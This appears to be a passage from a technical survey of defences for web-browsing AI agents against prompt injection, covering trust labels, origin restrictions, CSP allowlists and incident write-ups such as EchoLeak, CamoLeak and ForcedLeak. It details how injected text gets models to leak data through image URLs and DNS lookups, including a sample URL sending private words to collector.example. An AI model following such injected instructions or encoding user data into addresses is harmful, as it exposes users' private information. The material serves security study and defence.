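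Such an answer can be false even though it can't carry an instruction. In one of Nikolić and colleagues' examples, a user asks the agent to invite Marko to a code repository called "dotfiles". The agent can't see the repositories' names, so it asks the quarantined model about each one in turn until it finds the right one. An attacker's repository, placed first in the list, gets the model to answer yes, and the agent invites Marko to the wrong repository.

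Choudhary, Christodorescu and colleagues (2026) point out in *Secure-CUA* that an agent working from screenshots may also choose the right field but click the wrong one, because a misleading advertisement confuses the step that finds the field on the screen. Their system therefore hides untrusted regions during that step as well. It assumes that someone has correctly divided the page into trusted and untrusted parts.

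### The MicroNet test

Zverev and colleagues compared these defences on MicroNet, the network of 28 websites on which they tested SOPGuard. MicroNet has 56 attacks and 56 harmless tasks, 22 of which require data to cross origins. The attacks come from sites that the attacker runs, text that the attacker posts on a trusted site, and frames from third parties.

Fifty of the attacks inject instructions, and the other six inject false versions of data the agent needs for its task. The table gives the lowest and highest success rates across five models.

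| Defence | Injected instructions (50 attacks) | False data (6 attacks) | All 56 attacks |
|---|---|---|---|
| None | 58.0–97.6% | 40.0–80.0% | 57.5–95.7% |
| SOPGuard | 54.8–77.2% | 30.0–50.0% | 53.2–73.2% |
| Untrusted Content Masking | 0% | 43.3–63.3% | 4.6–6.8% |
| SPIDES | 0% | 0% | 0% |

In the test's 50 instruction attacks, the attacker chooses the model's output once the model has read the attacker's text, so the results don't estimate how often injections succeed against current models. For the six data attacks, the researchers used the models' real responses because they couldn't predict what queries the agent would send to the quarantined model.

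Masking does poorly on false data because it applies no further checks once the quarantined model has answered. SPIDES keeps the untrusted label on the answer, so the agent can't act on it at a trusted site without approval.

SPIDES's zero follows from its rules if the labels are correct and the user refuses every request an attack causes. MicroNet tests neither condition, because the researchers labelled the sites themselves and simulated a user who can always recognise an attack.

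### Recording which script wrote each element

Operators can label only what they know is on their pages. Iqbal points out that scripts from advertisers and other third parties create and change elements while a page is running, and that operators often don't know what those scripts will load. The browser doesn't keep track either, and treats anything an included third-party script writes into the page as the site's own.

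Iqbal's system, INTACT, tracks which scripts create or change the elements of a page. Before the page's own scripts start, it wraps the browser functions for doing so. When a script calls one of these functions, INTACT identifies the script from the list of code currently running. It marks an element as third-party if a third party's script created it or changed its text, its attributes or its response to events such as clicks. If INTACT can't identify the script, it treats the change as untrusted.

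In September 2026 Iqbal applied this method to the home pages of 1,270 websites. Browsers attribute an element to a third party only if it is in a third party's frame or loads something from a third party. By that standard, third parties accounted for 10% of the elements on an average page. By INTACT's records, the figure was 22.7%. Of all the elements that INTACT traced to third parties, the browser had attributed 58.7% to the site itself.

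Many of these elements are interactive. The browser missed 92.2% of the third-party elements that can submit a form and 90.3% of those that a user can type in. A host that hides third-party frames from the agent would still show it an advertisement that a script had written into the main page.

The 58.7% probably includes some false alarms, because INTACT identifies parties by their registered domains. For example, it counts samsclubimages.com as a third party on the Sam's Club site. Most third-party content is presumably harmless, so the figure measures how much content has an uncertain author, not how much is dangerous.

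INTACT's recording code runs inside the page, where a hostile script could tamper with it. Iqbal proposes moving the code into the browser. Lee, Chang and colleagues (2026) show in *WebMCP-Phalanx* that the browser must then distinguish scripts, not just origins. They studied tools that web pages offer to agents and gave each tool a credential, held by the script that registered it. This stopped one script from replacing or removing another's tools. But an advertiser's script could register its own tool and receive an equally valid credential, and the browser couldn't tell the advertiser's script from the site's own code.

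### Planning one element at a time

Knowing who wrote an element doesn't stop its text from influencing the model, which is why INTACT shows the model one element at a time. The system first splits the page into chunks of about 1,500 characters and has the model choose the one where it can best do the task. It then goes through that chunk element by element. Each time, the model sees only:

- the user's request;
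- the current element's own text and markup;
- a record of the actions chosen so far, without the text of the elements concerned;
- the element's position within a form, if it is in one.

The model decides whether the task needs this element and, if so, whether to click it, type in it or select something. Code attaches the decision to the element, so the model cannot name a different one. If a note on the page contains an instruction to click a link elsewhere, the model can at most propose a click on the note. The code rejects that click because plain text has no click action.

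In Iqbal's comparison with a conventional planner, which reads the whole page at once, INTACT's results depended heavily on what the attack asked for.

| What the attack asks for | Attacks | Conventional planner | INTACT |
|---|---|---|---|
| An action on another element | 545 | 74.1% | 1.5% |
| Data from the page, typed into the attacker's own field | 546 | 72.0% | 24.2% |
| All attacks | 1,091 | 73.1% | 12.8% |

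Iqbal instructed the model to obey injected text, so the 73.1% figure measures what a model would do once it follows such text, not how often a current model would follow it. INTACT's steps are also limited by a consent request, while the conventional planner's steps would run without one.

INTACT is weaker against the second kind of attack because the instruction is in the element the model is evaluating. In 101 of the 132 cases that got through, the model proposed only a click on the attacker's "Continue" button, which looked like the next step of a form. It never copied the data the attacker wanted, because that data was in another element, though in one case it guessed a single word of it.

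INTACT handles this case less well than SPIDES. It trusts whatever the site's own server and scripts deliver, which on a shop's site usually includes customer reviews. INTACT would therefore attribute a hostile review at Shop A to the shop. The review's text still couldn't cause a click elsewhere on the page, but the agent could follow a link in the review without the consent request that a third-party link would trigger.

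### Who supplies the labels

A third option is to have a model infer the labels, which requires no work from the site. But the model might read the attacker's text while deciding whether to trust it. Nikolić and colleagues avoid this by first removing all the text from the page, leaving only its structure. The model then looks for clues such as an element the site's developers named "post-content".

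In the researchers' tests on three sites, the model missed no groups of untrusted elements on Reddit, but missed 5.8% on Booking.com and 8.5% on GitLab. When they deliberately introduced such a mistake on GitLab by marking one untrusted element as trusted, the attack success rate rose from 0% to 6%. That was close to the 8% rate with a warning in the model's prompt instead. With no defence, the rate was 17%.

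*Prismata* (Villa, Ozdarendeli and colleagues, 2026) lets the model see some text, but only in a fixed order, from the outermost element inwards. The model settles each element's label before it sees what is inside. It can therefore read a heading such as "Customer Reviews" as a sign of untrusted content before it sees any review. Nothing inside an untrusted region can later receive a higher level of trust.

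A second check decides whether the task needs each button or link. The model making that decision sees only the button or link and the elements that contain it, so a review elsewhere on the page can't influence the result. In a sample of 90,408 pieces of untrusted content, only 94 (about 0.1%) both contained something the agent could click or fill in and had no earlier warning sign. Language models helped label this sample, so the figure depends partly on their accuracy. In tests with hostile pop-ups, Prismata reduced the average attack success rate from 85.5% to 0.7%.

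| Who supplies the labels | Systems | What they can identify | What they may miss |
|---|---|---|---|
| The site's operator | SPIDES, Untrusted Content Masking | Users' posts and, in SPIDES, private data and its permitted readers | Content that third-party scripts add later |
| Code that watches scripts | INTACT | Elements that third-party scripts write or change | Users' posts that the site delivers itself |
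| A model | Prismata, Untrusted Content Masking on unlabelled sites | Posts and advertisements in recognisable parts of a page | Content without a structural clue |

Iqbal objects that inferred labels bring back reliance on a model's judgement. That is true, but an attacker has less influence over a model that sees only the page's structure than over one that reads the whole page. The attacker can still look for places the model tends to mislabel.

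A host could also combine these methods, treating content as untrusted if the operator, the script records or the model labels it so. The host would then miss fewer attacks but hide more harmless content. Combining the methods would not produce reader sets, because neither a script's identity nor a page's structure shows which companies may receive a customer's address.

### Whether sites would add the labels

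SPIDES depends on website operators doing new work to benefit agents. Iqbal doubts that they will, because sites have been slow to adopt even established protections. His example is content security policy (CSP), in which a site lists where a page may load resources from and what it may connect to, and the browser enforces the list. CSP's designers described it in 2010, but according to CentralCSP, a company that scans websites for such policies, HTTP Archive found one on only 21.9% of mobile home pages in 2025.

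Many of the policies that do exist are weak. Report URI (2026) examined 170,057 of them in June and found that 46.8% allowed scripts written directly into the page, which undermines the protection against injected scripts. Adoption had more than doubled since 2022, so sites do respond eventually, though often with weak policies.

Zverev and colleagues compare their labels to accessibility markup, which describes a page's elements to screen readers and similar tools. They argue that the labels would not add much work for most operators, since sites commonly provide accessibility markup already. Accessibility surveys make the comparison less reassuring. WebAIM, which tests the home pages of the million most popular sites each year, found an average of 56.1 detectable errors per page in 2026, up from 51 in 2025. Ott (2026) notes in *This, Still Not for Everyone* that 95.9% of the pages had at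 least one detectable failure, compared with 97.8% in 2019.

Similar error rates in security labels would be serious. SPIDES treats unlabelled content on a trusted site as trusted and public, so if an operator forgot to label the reviews, the agent would trust them. The opposite default would be safer, but the agent could do very little on a site until the operator had labelled it.

Labeling may take less work than these comparisons suggest. Nikolić and colleagues needed only 15 to 30 rules per site to mark all the untrusted regions on GitLab, Booking.com and Reddit, and they cite an estimate that 3,000 domains receive half of all internet traffic. Labels also don't change how a page works for human visitors, whereas a strict CSP can break it.

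Someone other than the operator can also write labels. Nikolić and colleagues used a proxy, a program between the site and the browser, to add their own labels to GitLab's pages. A browser maker could do the same for popular sites, though it would have to update its labeling rules whenever a site changed its design.

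## Limiting which sites an agent may reach during a task

SPIDES and similar systems control what an agent may do with content it has read. A host can also restrict which sites the agent can reach, based on the user's request. In the laptop-shopping task, the agent has no reason to visit the user's bank site, so a host that blocks that site protects the account even after a hostile review has completely misled the model. Google announced such a system for Chrome in December 2025. Another system, ceLLMate, also controls what the agent can do within each site.

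### Agent Origin Sets

If an attacker misleads an agent that can visit any site, Parker explains, the result is effectively a bypass of site isolation, because the agent can carry data between all the sites where the user is logged in. Chrome's design therefore keeps two sets of origins for each session:

- **Read-only origins** are those whose content the model may receive.
- **Read-writable origins** are those where the agent may also act, for example by clicking or typing.

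When the planning model proposes an origin, a gating function checks whether the task needs it. Like the User Alignment Critic, this function doesn't receive web content, so a page cannot influence it directly. If an origin is in neither set, Chrome withholds its content from the model. For example, the user can see an advertisement in a frame from an unrelated origin, but Chrome doesn't pass it to the model.

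Chrome also has to check each way of reaching a new page. If the planning model chooses an address on a new origin, a variant of the Critic judges whether the address is relevant before Chrome adds the origin and opens the page. The same variant checks the destination when a page moves to a new origin by itself.

The user can share other open pages with the agent. The planning model can use their content, but it still needs the gating function's approval to add an origin. For tools outside the web, Chrome separates read calls from write calls and checks that each call suits the task.

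### The data flows that remain

If the mail and the notes in the shopping task are web pages, the agent needs write access to all four sites, even the mailbox, because searching it means typing and opening a message usually means clicking. The sets don't distinguish these clicks from the one that sends a message.

If an agent can read m origins during a task and can also write to w of them, data can move from one origin to another in w(m − 1) ways. With four origins, all writable, there are 12 ways, of which the task needs only four.

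| Data from | To Shop A | To Shop B | To the mail | To the notes |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Shop A | – | Possible | Possible | Needed |
| Shop B | Possible | – | Possible | Needed |
| Mail | Needed | Needed | – | Possible |
| Notes | Possible | Possible | Possible | – |

The sets keep the agent away from the bank and from any site the attacker runs. But a misled agent could still email the user's notes to the attacker, since the mail site accepts any recipient. Chrome's agent tries to pause for the user before it sends a message, which is a separate safeguard against this theft. If the user opened the message containing the delivery address and shared that page with the agent, the mail site could stay read-only. That would remove the three flows into the mail site and leave nine.

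Even the flows that are necessary for the task are broader than they have to be, because the path that carries the delivery address to Shop A could also carry a private message.

### What Chrome has released

Parker wrote that Google's first version tracked only the design's read-writable set, because the team found it hard to set the right limits before seeing how they affected real tasks. That version could not mark a site as readable but not writable. Roesner and Kohlbrenner tested Chrome with Gemini in early 2026 and found that it read frames from other origins, so either Chrome was not yet hiding unrelated frames or it had classified these as relevant.

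In August 2026, Berschadski described a single limit, which confines the agent to origins relevant to the immediate task. For companies, Chrome also applies an employee's access restrictions to their agent.

Chrome's public source code gives more detail. By June 2026, the file that controls an agent's navigation, Chromium (2025), contained these checks, in this order:

1. The browser consults the employer's policy and then a safety list. If either one allows or blocks the destination, that settles the matter.
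2. If the destination has the same origin as the current page, the browser allows the move.
3. If the destination is on a list of sensitive sites, the browser asks the user, unless the user has already confirmed that origin during the task.
4. If the task's record of allowed origins includes the destination, the browser allows the move.
5. Any other destination counts as a new origin. Depending on its settings, the browser allows the move, asks the user or asks Google's server.

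The settings file (Chromium, 2025) turns on the request for sensitive sites but turns off confirmation of new origins. With these defaults, a page can take the agent to any unfamiliar site that isn't on a sensitive or blocked list, so Step 5 provides none of the vetting that Parker described for pages that navigate by themselves.

What users get may differ from these defaults, because Google can change such settings remotely and its servers may check an origin before telling the browser to go there. The code in Chromium (2025) lets the browser receive additional writable origins for a task, which would be consistent with such server checks. The code also applies the navigation check only to the main page, so frames need a separate control.

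Comments in Chromium (2025) describe a trial mode in which the browser checks each new origin with the server but only logs the result. Google could use this mode to measure how often enforcement would interrupt tasks.

### How ceLLMate works

Agent Origin Sets treat every click on a writable site the same way. *CELLMATE* (Meng, Feng and colleagues, 2025) describes a browser extension that can distinguish a purchase from a search.

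Rules about clicks would be unreliable, because a click at the same position on the screen may open an email or delete it, depending on the page. Rules about the agent's tools can also fail. When the researchers barred an agent from navigating directly to Hacker News, it searched for the site on DuckDuckGo and clicked the result.

ceLLMate instead checks the HTTP requests that the browser sends to websites. Whatever sequence of clicks leads to an order, the shop eventually receives a request to place it. To recognise that request, ceLLMate uses an agent sitemap, a file in which a site lists its security-relevant requests and what each one does. The site or a trusted third party then writes policies for these actions. The researchers' example for Amazon includes three:

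| Request | Action in the sitemap | Policy |
|---|---|---|
| Fetch the cart page | View the cart | Allow |
| Send a change to the cart | Update the cart | Allow |
| Submit the checkout page | Place an order | Allow if the total is within a set limit |

The order request doesn't contain the total, so the sitemap records where the total appears on the checkout page and ceLLMate reads it there. A $50 limit would still allow two $49 orders, so ceLLMate can also count requests and allow only one order.

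The system chooses a policy for each task as follows:

1. A model reads the user's request and lists the sites it names.
2. For each site, the model receives the request and descriptions of the available policies. It selects the smallest set that the task needs and fills in values such as a price limit.
3. The user reviews the selection and can change it.
4. The extension enforces the selection until the user changes it. It blocks requests to unrelated sites, apart from servers that the permitted sites need, such as those that store their images.

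In the shopping task, ceLLMate could let the agent search and read the mail but not send or delete anything. This would prevent the agent from emailing the notes to an attacker. On the shops' sites, it could allow searches and delivery quotes but not orders.

A private message could still reach Shop A through its delivery form, because the form is part of the task and ceLLMate doesn't track where the text came from. A conditional policy could accept only one address, but the model that selects the policy would need the address beforehand, and in this example the address is somewhere in the mailbox.

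### Tests of ceLLMate

Meng and colleagues based their attack test on WASP, a benchmark of prompt injections against web agents. WASP's injections succeeded less than 17% of the time against OpenAI's o1 and less than 7% against the other models they tried, so blocking them would have proved little. The researchers instead wrote scripts that carried out all 12 of WASP's attacker goals on GitLab, a site for managing code, as if the attacker fully controlled the agent. The goals included deleting projects, stealing access tokens and registering the attacker's login key.

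The user's task was to comment on an issue or upvote it. A model correctly selected permission to read and write issues, and ceLLMate blocked all 12 attacks. Rewording an injection would not change this result, because the test assumed the injection had already worked.

However, every attack tested needed an action that the policy didn't allow. The researchers left out WASP's attacks on Reddit, most of which involve phishing or harassment through ordinary comments. ceLLMate would have to allow such comments if the task involved commenting. On GitLab, a misled agent could also copy text from a private issue into a public comment without exceeding its permissions.

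The researchers also tested how well models select policies, using 209 tasks on shopping, travel and code-management sites. Only some tasks also required the model to fill in a value, and the last column covers the 32 such tasks on shopping sites.

| Model | Correct policies | Correct policies and values |
|---|---|---|
| GPT-5.1 | 201 of 209 (96.2%) | 27 of 32 (84.4%) |
| Gemini 2.5 Pro | 204 of 209 (97.6%) | 26 of 32 (81.3%) |
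| Claude Opus 4.5 | 207 of 209 (99.0%) | 31 of 32 (96.9%) |

Some errors only stop the agent from finishing, as when one model omitted permission to rename a list that the user wanted renamed. Other errors give an attacker more to exploit, such as granting unneeded permissions for a task that creates a code repository. One model also confused a wishlist with a shopping cart and let the agent add to the cart instead of the wishlist.

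In a separate test of whether the models could name the right sites, accuracy ranged from 93.1% to 100%. When a request named no site, the models occasionally guessed one. For example, they often chose Sony's website for a question about a Sony television.

These are good results for models from 2025, but the tasks were easier than many real requests. The researchers had rewritten vague tasks to add details and limits, and each policy-selection task involved only one site. If a model chose correctly for each site 97.6% of the time, independently of the others, it would get all four sites right in about 91% of tasks like the shopping one. The user would have to catch the remaining mistakes during review.

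### Judging which sites are relevant

Both systems enforce their limits in code, but a model decides what the limits should be. Both keep web pages away from that model.

ceLLMate offers the stronger protection here because it settles the permissions before the agent opens any page, and nothing the agent reads can extend them. But this rules out tasks in which the agent has to discover the right site. If a user asks for a coffee maker without naming a shop, ceLLMate grants no access. The shopping request would fail for the same reason unless the user named both shops.

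Chrome's agent can request new origins during the task, so it can follow a search result to an unfamiliar shop. By the time it makes such a request, however, the planning model may have read a hostile page. The gating function receives no page content, so an attacker's site might pass as relevant if its name suggests delivery quotes for laptops. Parker gives no error rate for the gating function.

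### Hostile content on an allowed site

A site can be relevant to the task and still contain an attack. Shop A has to be in the read-writable set, so its reviews reach the model along with everything else on its pages. Third-party text that scripts write into the page also passes the origin check, and Iqbal found such text to be common. Chrome relies on other safeguards for these cases, including a classifier that checks every page the agent sees for injections.

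ceLLMate doesn't filter what the model reads. It applies the same limits to the agent's requests whoever wrote the text that prompted them. This can stop some attacks within a single site, such as the one in which Zverev and colleagues used a direct message to make an agent publish the user's recovery address. An agent that needs to click through messages has write access to the whole social network under Agent Origin Sets, including the user's profile. With ceLLMate, a policy for reading messages would not permit changes to the profile, provided that the sitemap lists them as a separate action.

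### Work for site owners

Agent Origin Sets need nothing from websites, while ceLLMate needs a sitemap and a set of policies for each site, which someone has to update when the site changes.

Meng and colleagues compare writing a sitemap to documenting a programming interface, and argue that companies have good reason to protect their customers. They built a 51-entry sitemap for GitLab by hand from the GitLab code that maps web addresses to functions, and suggest that developers could automate this for common web frameworks. Trusted outsiders could also write policies, much as the EasyList project maintains filter lists for ad blockers, but an outsider who cannot see a site's code may miss some of its actions. Where a sitemap is incomplete or wrong, users have only the protection they would have had without ceLLMate.

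The slow spread of content security policy suggests that many sites would not publish a sitemap soon. Meng and colleagues similarly doubt that websites will quickly offer MCP tools to agents, since most sites took about two decades to adopt encrypted connections. A sitemap requires less change to a site than MCP tools do, but its adoption could also be slow.

### A policy that changes with each request

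The same-origin policy depends on the addresses involved, not on what the user is trying to do. Browser developers can therefore specify the correct result for a pair of origins and test for it. If the test fails, they can fix the bug for everyone.

A policy inferred from the task has no fixed standard of correctness. Shop B belongs on the list of allowed sites when the user wants to compare prices, but not when the user asks about an order at Shop A. In ceLLMate's benchmark, two researchers independently chose the minimum permissions for each task, then resolved disagreements by refining the tasks and policies. Even the most accurate model chose differently from them in about 1% of tasks. A browser that misapplied the same-origin policy that often would have a serious vulnerability.

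Fixed rules avoid this problem but, like Trail of Bits' rule, often fit agents' tasks poorly. A fixed list of allowed sites works better when someone knows in advance which sites a task requires. Chromium (2026) applies such a list to sessions that use Chrome's developer tools. If whoever starts the browser supplies a list of allowed addresses, Chrome blocks navigation to any other address, and no model has to judge whether a site is relevant. A company could do much the same for an agent that only collects invoices from known suppliers, but nobody can write such a list for a personal assistant that may receive any request.

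## Allowlists for outgoing data in content that assistants render

Chrome's Agent Origin Sets and ceLLMate limit the sites an agent may visit or act on. But a host can also send data to a site the agent never opens, because displaying the model's answer can make the user's browser contact other servers.

### How an answer leaks data without a tool call

Most chat assistants write their answers in Markdown, a plain-text notation for headings, links and images. The interface converts the Markdown to HTML, which the browser displays. Markdown gives only an image's address, and the browser normally fetches the image from there as soon as it displays the answer.

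The request gives the server the whole address, including everything after the host name. In the laptop-shopping task, a hostile review at Shop A could lead the model to end its price comparison with an image at an address like this:

`https://collector.example/pixel.png?text=clinic-appointment-friday`

Whoever runs `collector.example` can then open the server's log and read the words from the private message. The image can be one transparent pixel, so the user notices nothing.

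Approvals and other checks on proposed actions don't stop an image in the assistant's answer from sending data out, because the model has only written its final answer and hasn't proposed an action. The same-origin policy doesn't stop it either, since a page may display images from other origins. A link in the answer can also send data out, but only if the user clicks it.

The security researcher Johann Rehberger reported the technique to OpenAI and Microsoft in early 2023, according to *OpenAI Explains URL-Based Data Exfiltration Mitigations in New Paper* on his blog, Embrace The Red. Microsoft fixed Bing Chat that May with a content security policy. Willison's *GitHub Copilot Chat* (2024) lists earlier examples of the same flaw in ChatGPT, Google Bard, Writer.com, Amazon Q and Google NotebookLM.

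### What a content security policy blocks

A site sends its content security policy (CSP) along with the page, as a series of directives that each cover one kind of load or connection. An assistant at `https://chat.example` might use this policy:

```
default-src 'none';
script-src 'self';
img-src 'self' https://images.shop-a.example;
connect-src 'self';
form-action 'self'
```

| Directive | Effect |
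|---|---|
| `default-src 'none'` | Blocks every kind of resource that has no directive of its own here, such as fonts, video and frames |
| `script-src 'self'` | Allows script files from `chat.example` only, and no scripts written directly into the page |
| `img-src` | Allows images from `chat.example` and from Shop A's image server |
| `connect-src 'self'` | Lets the page's scripts exchange data only with `chat.example` |
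| `form-action 'self'` | Lets forms on the page submit only to `chat.example`; `default-src` does not cover forms |

The browser loads any photograph from `images.shop-a.example` that appears in the model's answer. It never requests the image from `collector.example` because `img-src` has no matching entry, so the private words stay on the user's machine.

This check on images comes close to meeting Anderson's requirements for a reference monitor. The browser applies it to every image load, and no text in the context can change the policy, which arrived with the page. The check is also simple, because it mainly compares host names. An entry can include a path, but the browser ignores any text after a question mark when it compares URLs, and the stolen words were there in this example.

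The policy does not restrict links, so a user who clicks a hostile link still sends any data contained in its address. Redirects are less of a problem because if an allowed server redirects the browser to another site, the browser checks the new address too. The browser can't check what an allowed server does with a request after receiving it.

### Allowed services that relay requests

Microsoft 365 Copilot answers employees' questions using their company's mail, files and chats. In 2025, researchers at Aim Labs showed that an outsider could take data from it by sending an employee one email, in an attack they named EchoLeak. Ravia (2025), in *Breaking down 'EchoLeak', the First Zero-Click AI Vulnerability Enabling Data Exfiltration*, traces the path:

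1. The attacker's email contains instructions worded as if for its human recipient. Microsoft's injection classifier lets it through.
2. The employee asks Copilot about something at work. Copilot retrieves the email together with internal material. The email covers many office topics, which makes its retrieval more likely.
3. The model adds an image to its answer, with internal data in the address. Copilot normally removes external images, but its filter misses a less common Markdown notation.
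4. The image's address belongs to a Microsoft Teams service that the CSP allows. The service accepts a second address as part of the request and fetches it from Microsoft's servers. The second address is the attacker's, and it contains the data.

The browser correctly allowed a request to Teams, but the policy did not apply to the request that Teams then made. The researchers had first found a similar relay in SharePoint, but it worked only if the employee accepted an invitation to the attacker's site.

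The attacker needed no account at the company (Reddy and Gujral, 2025, *EchoLeak*). According to Infosecurity Magazine's *Microsoft 365 Copilot*, Aim Labs contacted Microsoft in January 2025, Microsoft finished its patch in May, and the findings came out on June 11. Microsoft told the researchers that the flaw had affected no customers.

Ravia also published the policy's list of image sources. It had 29 different entries, including 11 wildcards, which allow every subdomain of a domain. One was `*.bing.com`, which another team used a year later to get data out. Varonis' *SearchLeak* (June 15, 2026) describes an attack on Copilot's enterprise search that starts when an employee clicks a link to a genuine Microsoft address. The link contains a search query, which Copilot treats as a prompt. The model searches the employee's mail and writes an image address containing what it finds. The address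 points to Bing's image search, which fetches pictures from addresses that users supply, so Bing passes the data to the attacker's server.

Copilot's safeguard against such images wrapped each answer so that the browser would treat any HTML as plain text, but only once the answer was complete. While the answer was still arriving, the browser briefly rendered the raw HTML and sent the request.

Microsoft has since fixed SearchLeak on its own servers. The Hacker News (2026) notes that Varonis presented a demonstration, not an attack seen in use. It also notes that Microsoft labelled the flaw critical but scored it 6.5 out of 10, while the US National Vulnerability Database gave it 7.5.

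Varonis advises companies to check their allowlists for domains that fetch user-supplied URLs. This advice is sound but hard to follow when a list has 11 wildcards, because each wildcard covers services that other teams run and may change at any time.

### Expired domains and shared hosting

An allowlist entry can also become unsafe when a domain changes owner. An attack called ForcedLeak exploited this problem in Salesforce's Agentforce, which runs AI agents on a company's customer records. The attacker filled in a public contact form, and Salesforce stored the submission as a sales lead. When an employee later asked the agent about that lead, the model followed instructions in the submission and wrote an image address containing other leads' email addresses.

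The CSP failed to block the image because it still allowed a domain under `my-salesforce-cms.com` after Salesforce's registration of that name had expired (Willison, 2025). Researchers at Noma Security registered the name and received the data.

ForcedLeak was reported to Salesforce on July 28, 2025, fixed on September 8 and made public on September 25, according to ThaiCERT's *ForcedLeak Vulnerability in Salesforce Agentforce Risks CRM Data Exposure via Prompt Injection*. Salesforce recovered the domain and, The Hacker News (2025) reports, began enforcing a list of trusted addresses on the agents' output. This list is another allowlist, so the fix depends on Salesforce keeping it up to date.

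Even a domain that hasn't changed hands may host content from millions of other people. Superhuman, an email application with an AI assistant, allowed requests to `docs.google.com`, where anyone can create a Google Form. A form's owner can create a URL that submits a response when opened. PromptArmor's *Superhuman AI Exfiltrates Emails* describes an attack that begins when the user asks for a summary of recent mail. An injection in one unopened message makes the model write an image whose URL submits the contents of the user's mail to the attacker's form. The policy allows the browser to request the image from Google, which records the contents as a form response.

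One answer leaked the full text of several messages, and another leaked parts of more than 40. PromptArmor, a security company, reported the flaw on Friday, December 5, 2025. Superhuman disabled the affected features on Monday and deployed its first patch on Tuesday. The two companies disclosed the case on January 12, 2026, after further repairs.

Google's own chatbot, Bard, had failed in much the same way in 2023. Its policy limited images to `*.google.com`, but Willison's *Hacking Google Bard* describes how an attacker could host a program on `script.google.com` to receive the data. Both policies named only Google's domains, so they allowed requests to any Google customer's forms or scripts, including the attacker's. An entry with a path could allow only one particular form, but the site would have to know in advance which forms it needed.

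Web researchers had already documented this weakness in allowlists for scripts. In *CSP Is Dead, Long Live CSP!* (2016), Weichselbaum and colleagues examined policies across the web. Of the 15 domains that sites most often allowed as script sources, 14 hosted something an attacker could use to bypass the policy. About 76% of the distinct policies had a script allowlist that an attacker could bypass this way. The paper recommended that sites stop listing domains and mark each permitted script with a random value that changes every time the page loads. This works for scripts because a site's developers know which ones they wrote, but an assistant's host doesn't know in advance which images belong in an answer. If the host marked every image the model writes, it would also approve any that an attacker got the model to include.

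### CamoLeak and the trusted image proxy

GitHub's design was stricter. Its CSP blocked images from domains that GitHub did not own, so external images could reach the page only through Camo, GitHub's image proxy. When a user saves a document with an external image, GitHub replaces the image's address with a Camo address that contains a cryptographic signature. Camo fetches the image only if the signature is valid. A model can't compute the signature, so it can't create a valid new Camo address that contains private text.

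Legit Security's *CamoLeak* describes how its researcher still leaked data from GitHub Copilot Chat in June 2025. He used GitHub's normal interface to get valid Camo addresses for images on his own server, one for each letter and symbol. He put the addresses and his instructions in a hidden comment on a pull request, a proposed change to a project's code. When another user asked Copilot about the pull request, the model looked up private material with that user's permissions and spelled it out as a row of invisible images. Each image request revealed one character to his server.

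He used this method to obtain the description of an unpublished security flaw from a private project. He also had Copilot search a user's code for an access key and leak the result. GitHub had created every address, so the signatures were valid, but the model encoded the secret in which addresses it used and in what order.

GitHub had turned off all images in Copilot Chat by August 14, 2025, which fixed the flaw. The press coverage in the OECD's *GitHub Copilot Chat Vulnerability Exposes Private Code and Secrets* (2025) begins on October 8.

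### How much data a choice of addresses can carry

An allowlist limits where requests can go, but data can still leak if an attacker can observe some difference at a permitted destination. If the attacker can tell apart requests to N addresses, each request can carry up to log₂ N bits, and k requests in a known order can express N^k different messages. The table applies this to a six-digit login code, which has a million possible values.

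| Addresses the attacker can tell apart | Bits per request | Requests needed for the code |
|---|---|---|
| 2 | 1 | 20 |
| 10 | 3.3 | 6 |
| 36 (letters and digits) | 5.2 | 4 |
| 1,000 | 10.0 | 2 |
| 1,000,000 | 19.9 | 1 |

Even a single address can carry one bit of information, because the model can either load it or not. That bit could reveal whether a mailbox contains a message from a particular clinic.

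OpenAI ran into this problem after it stopped ChatGPT from adding text to web addresses found in outside content. Radware's *ZombieAgent* describes how the security company got around this restriction by putting a complete set of fixed addresses in an email. When the user asked ChatGPT to do something with their Gmail account, the model opened the addresses that spelled out the private text. Requests can arrive out of order, so Radware prepared a separate address for each combination of character and position, which takes 360 addresses for text of up to ten letters and digits.

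In the main version of the attack, OpenAI's servers opened the addresses, so a CSP in the user's browser would not have blocked the requests. Radware reported the flaw on September 26, 2025, and OpenAI fixed it on December 16.

### Search queries and domain-name lookups

Data can leak without any request to a site the attacker controls. In one of Trail of Bits' attacks, the agent only ran a Google search, with a query that combined the private text with very unusual search terms. Trail of Bits could then read the query in Google Search Console, which shows website owners which searches led to their pages. An allowlist for an assistant with web search almost has to include the search engine, and would therefore permit this attack.

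Domain-name lookups are harder to notice. Before a computer contacts `www.shop-a.example`, it looks up the numerical address for that name through the domain name system (DNS). It sends the name to a resolver, which may forward the query to the domain owner's name server. An attacker who owns a domain can therefore receive data as part of a made-up name under that domain, even if the computer never connects to the attacker's site.

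Trail of Bits used made-up Wikipedia subdomains, which the agent's allowlist permitted. DNS lookups for these names go to Wikipedia's name servers rather than the attacker's, so the attacker also has to observe the user's unencrypted DNS traffic. That makes the attack less practical than an image leak, though the operator of a public wireless network could do it.

Lookups had also undermined CSP on ordinary pages. To save time, browsers look up domain names that appear in a page before the user clicks anything. Van Acker and colleagues found in *Data Exfiltration in the Face of CSP* (2016) that a page could often leak data through these early lookups in popular browsers, despite its policy.

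Check Point Research's *ChatGPT Data Leakage via a Hidden Outbound Channel* (2026) describes a DNS leak from the sandbox where ChatGPT runs code. The sandbox blocked direct internet connections but still resolved domain names. The attack began when the user pasted a malicious prompt into the chat, perhaps from a website that recommends prompts, or used a customised version of ChatGPT that an attacker had built. The model then ran code that encoded parts of the conversation in domain names and looked them up.

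In one demonstration, a user uploaded laboratory results to a customised ChatGPT that acted as a doctor. The researchers' server received the patient's name and the model's medical assessment. ChatGPT normally asks for approval before a customised version sends data to an outside service, but it did not ask here, and it told the user that the file had not been sent anywhere. The researchers could also use the channel to send commands into the sandbox. OpenAI had already found the underlying problem itself and finished deploying a fix on February 20, 2026.

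### Checking exact addresses against a public index

OpenAI's first defence against data leaks through URLs, introduced in December 2023, was a function that classified a URL as safe or unsafe. Tenable (2025) bypassed it with `bing.com` links that redirect to other sites, which the function accepted because it treated `bing.com` as safe.

OpenAI's *Keeping your data safe when an AI agent clicks a link* (2026), published on January 28, gives redirects as one reason for not relying on a list of trusted sites. Its other reason is that a strict list produces many false alarms, which teach users to click through warnings. OpenAI instead checks whether the exact address is already public:

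1. A crawler, working much like a search engine's, records addresses it finds on the public web. It has no access to users' conversations or accounts.
2. Before ChatGPT fetches an address automatically, the host looks for an exact match in this index.
3. If there is a match, ChatGPT may open the page or display the image.
4. If there is none, the host either tells the agent to try another site or shows the user the address with a warning that it may contain information from the conversation.

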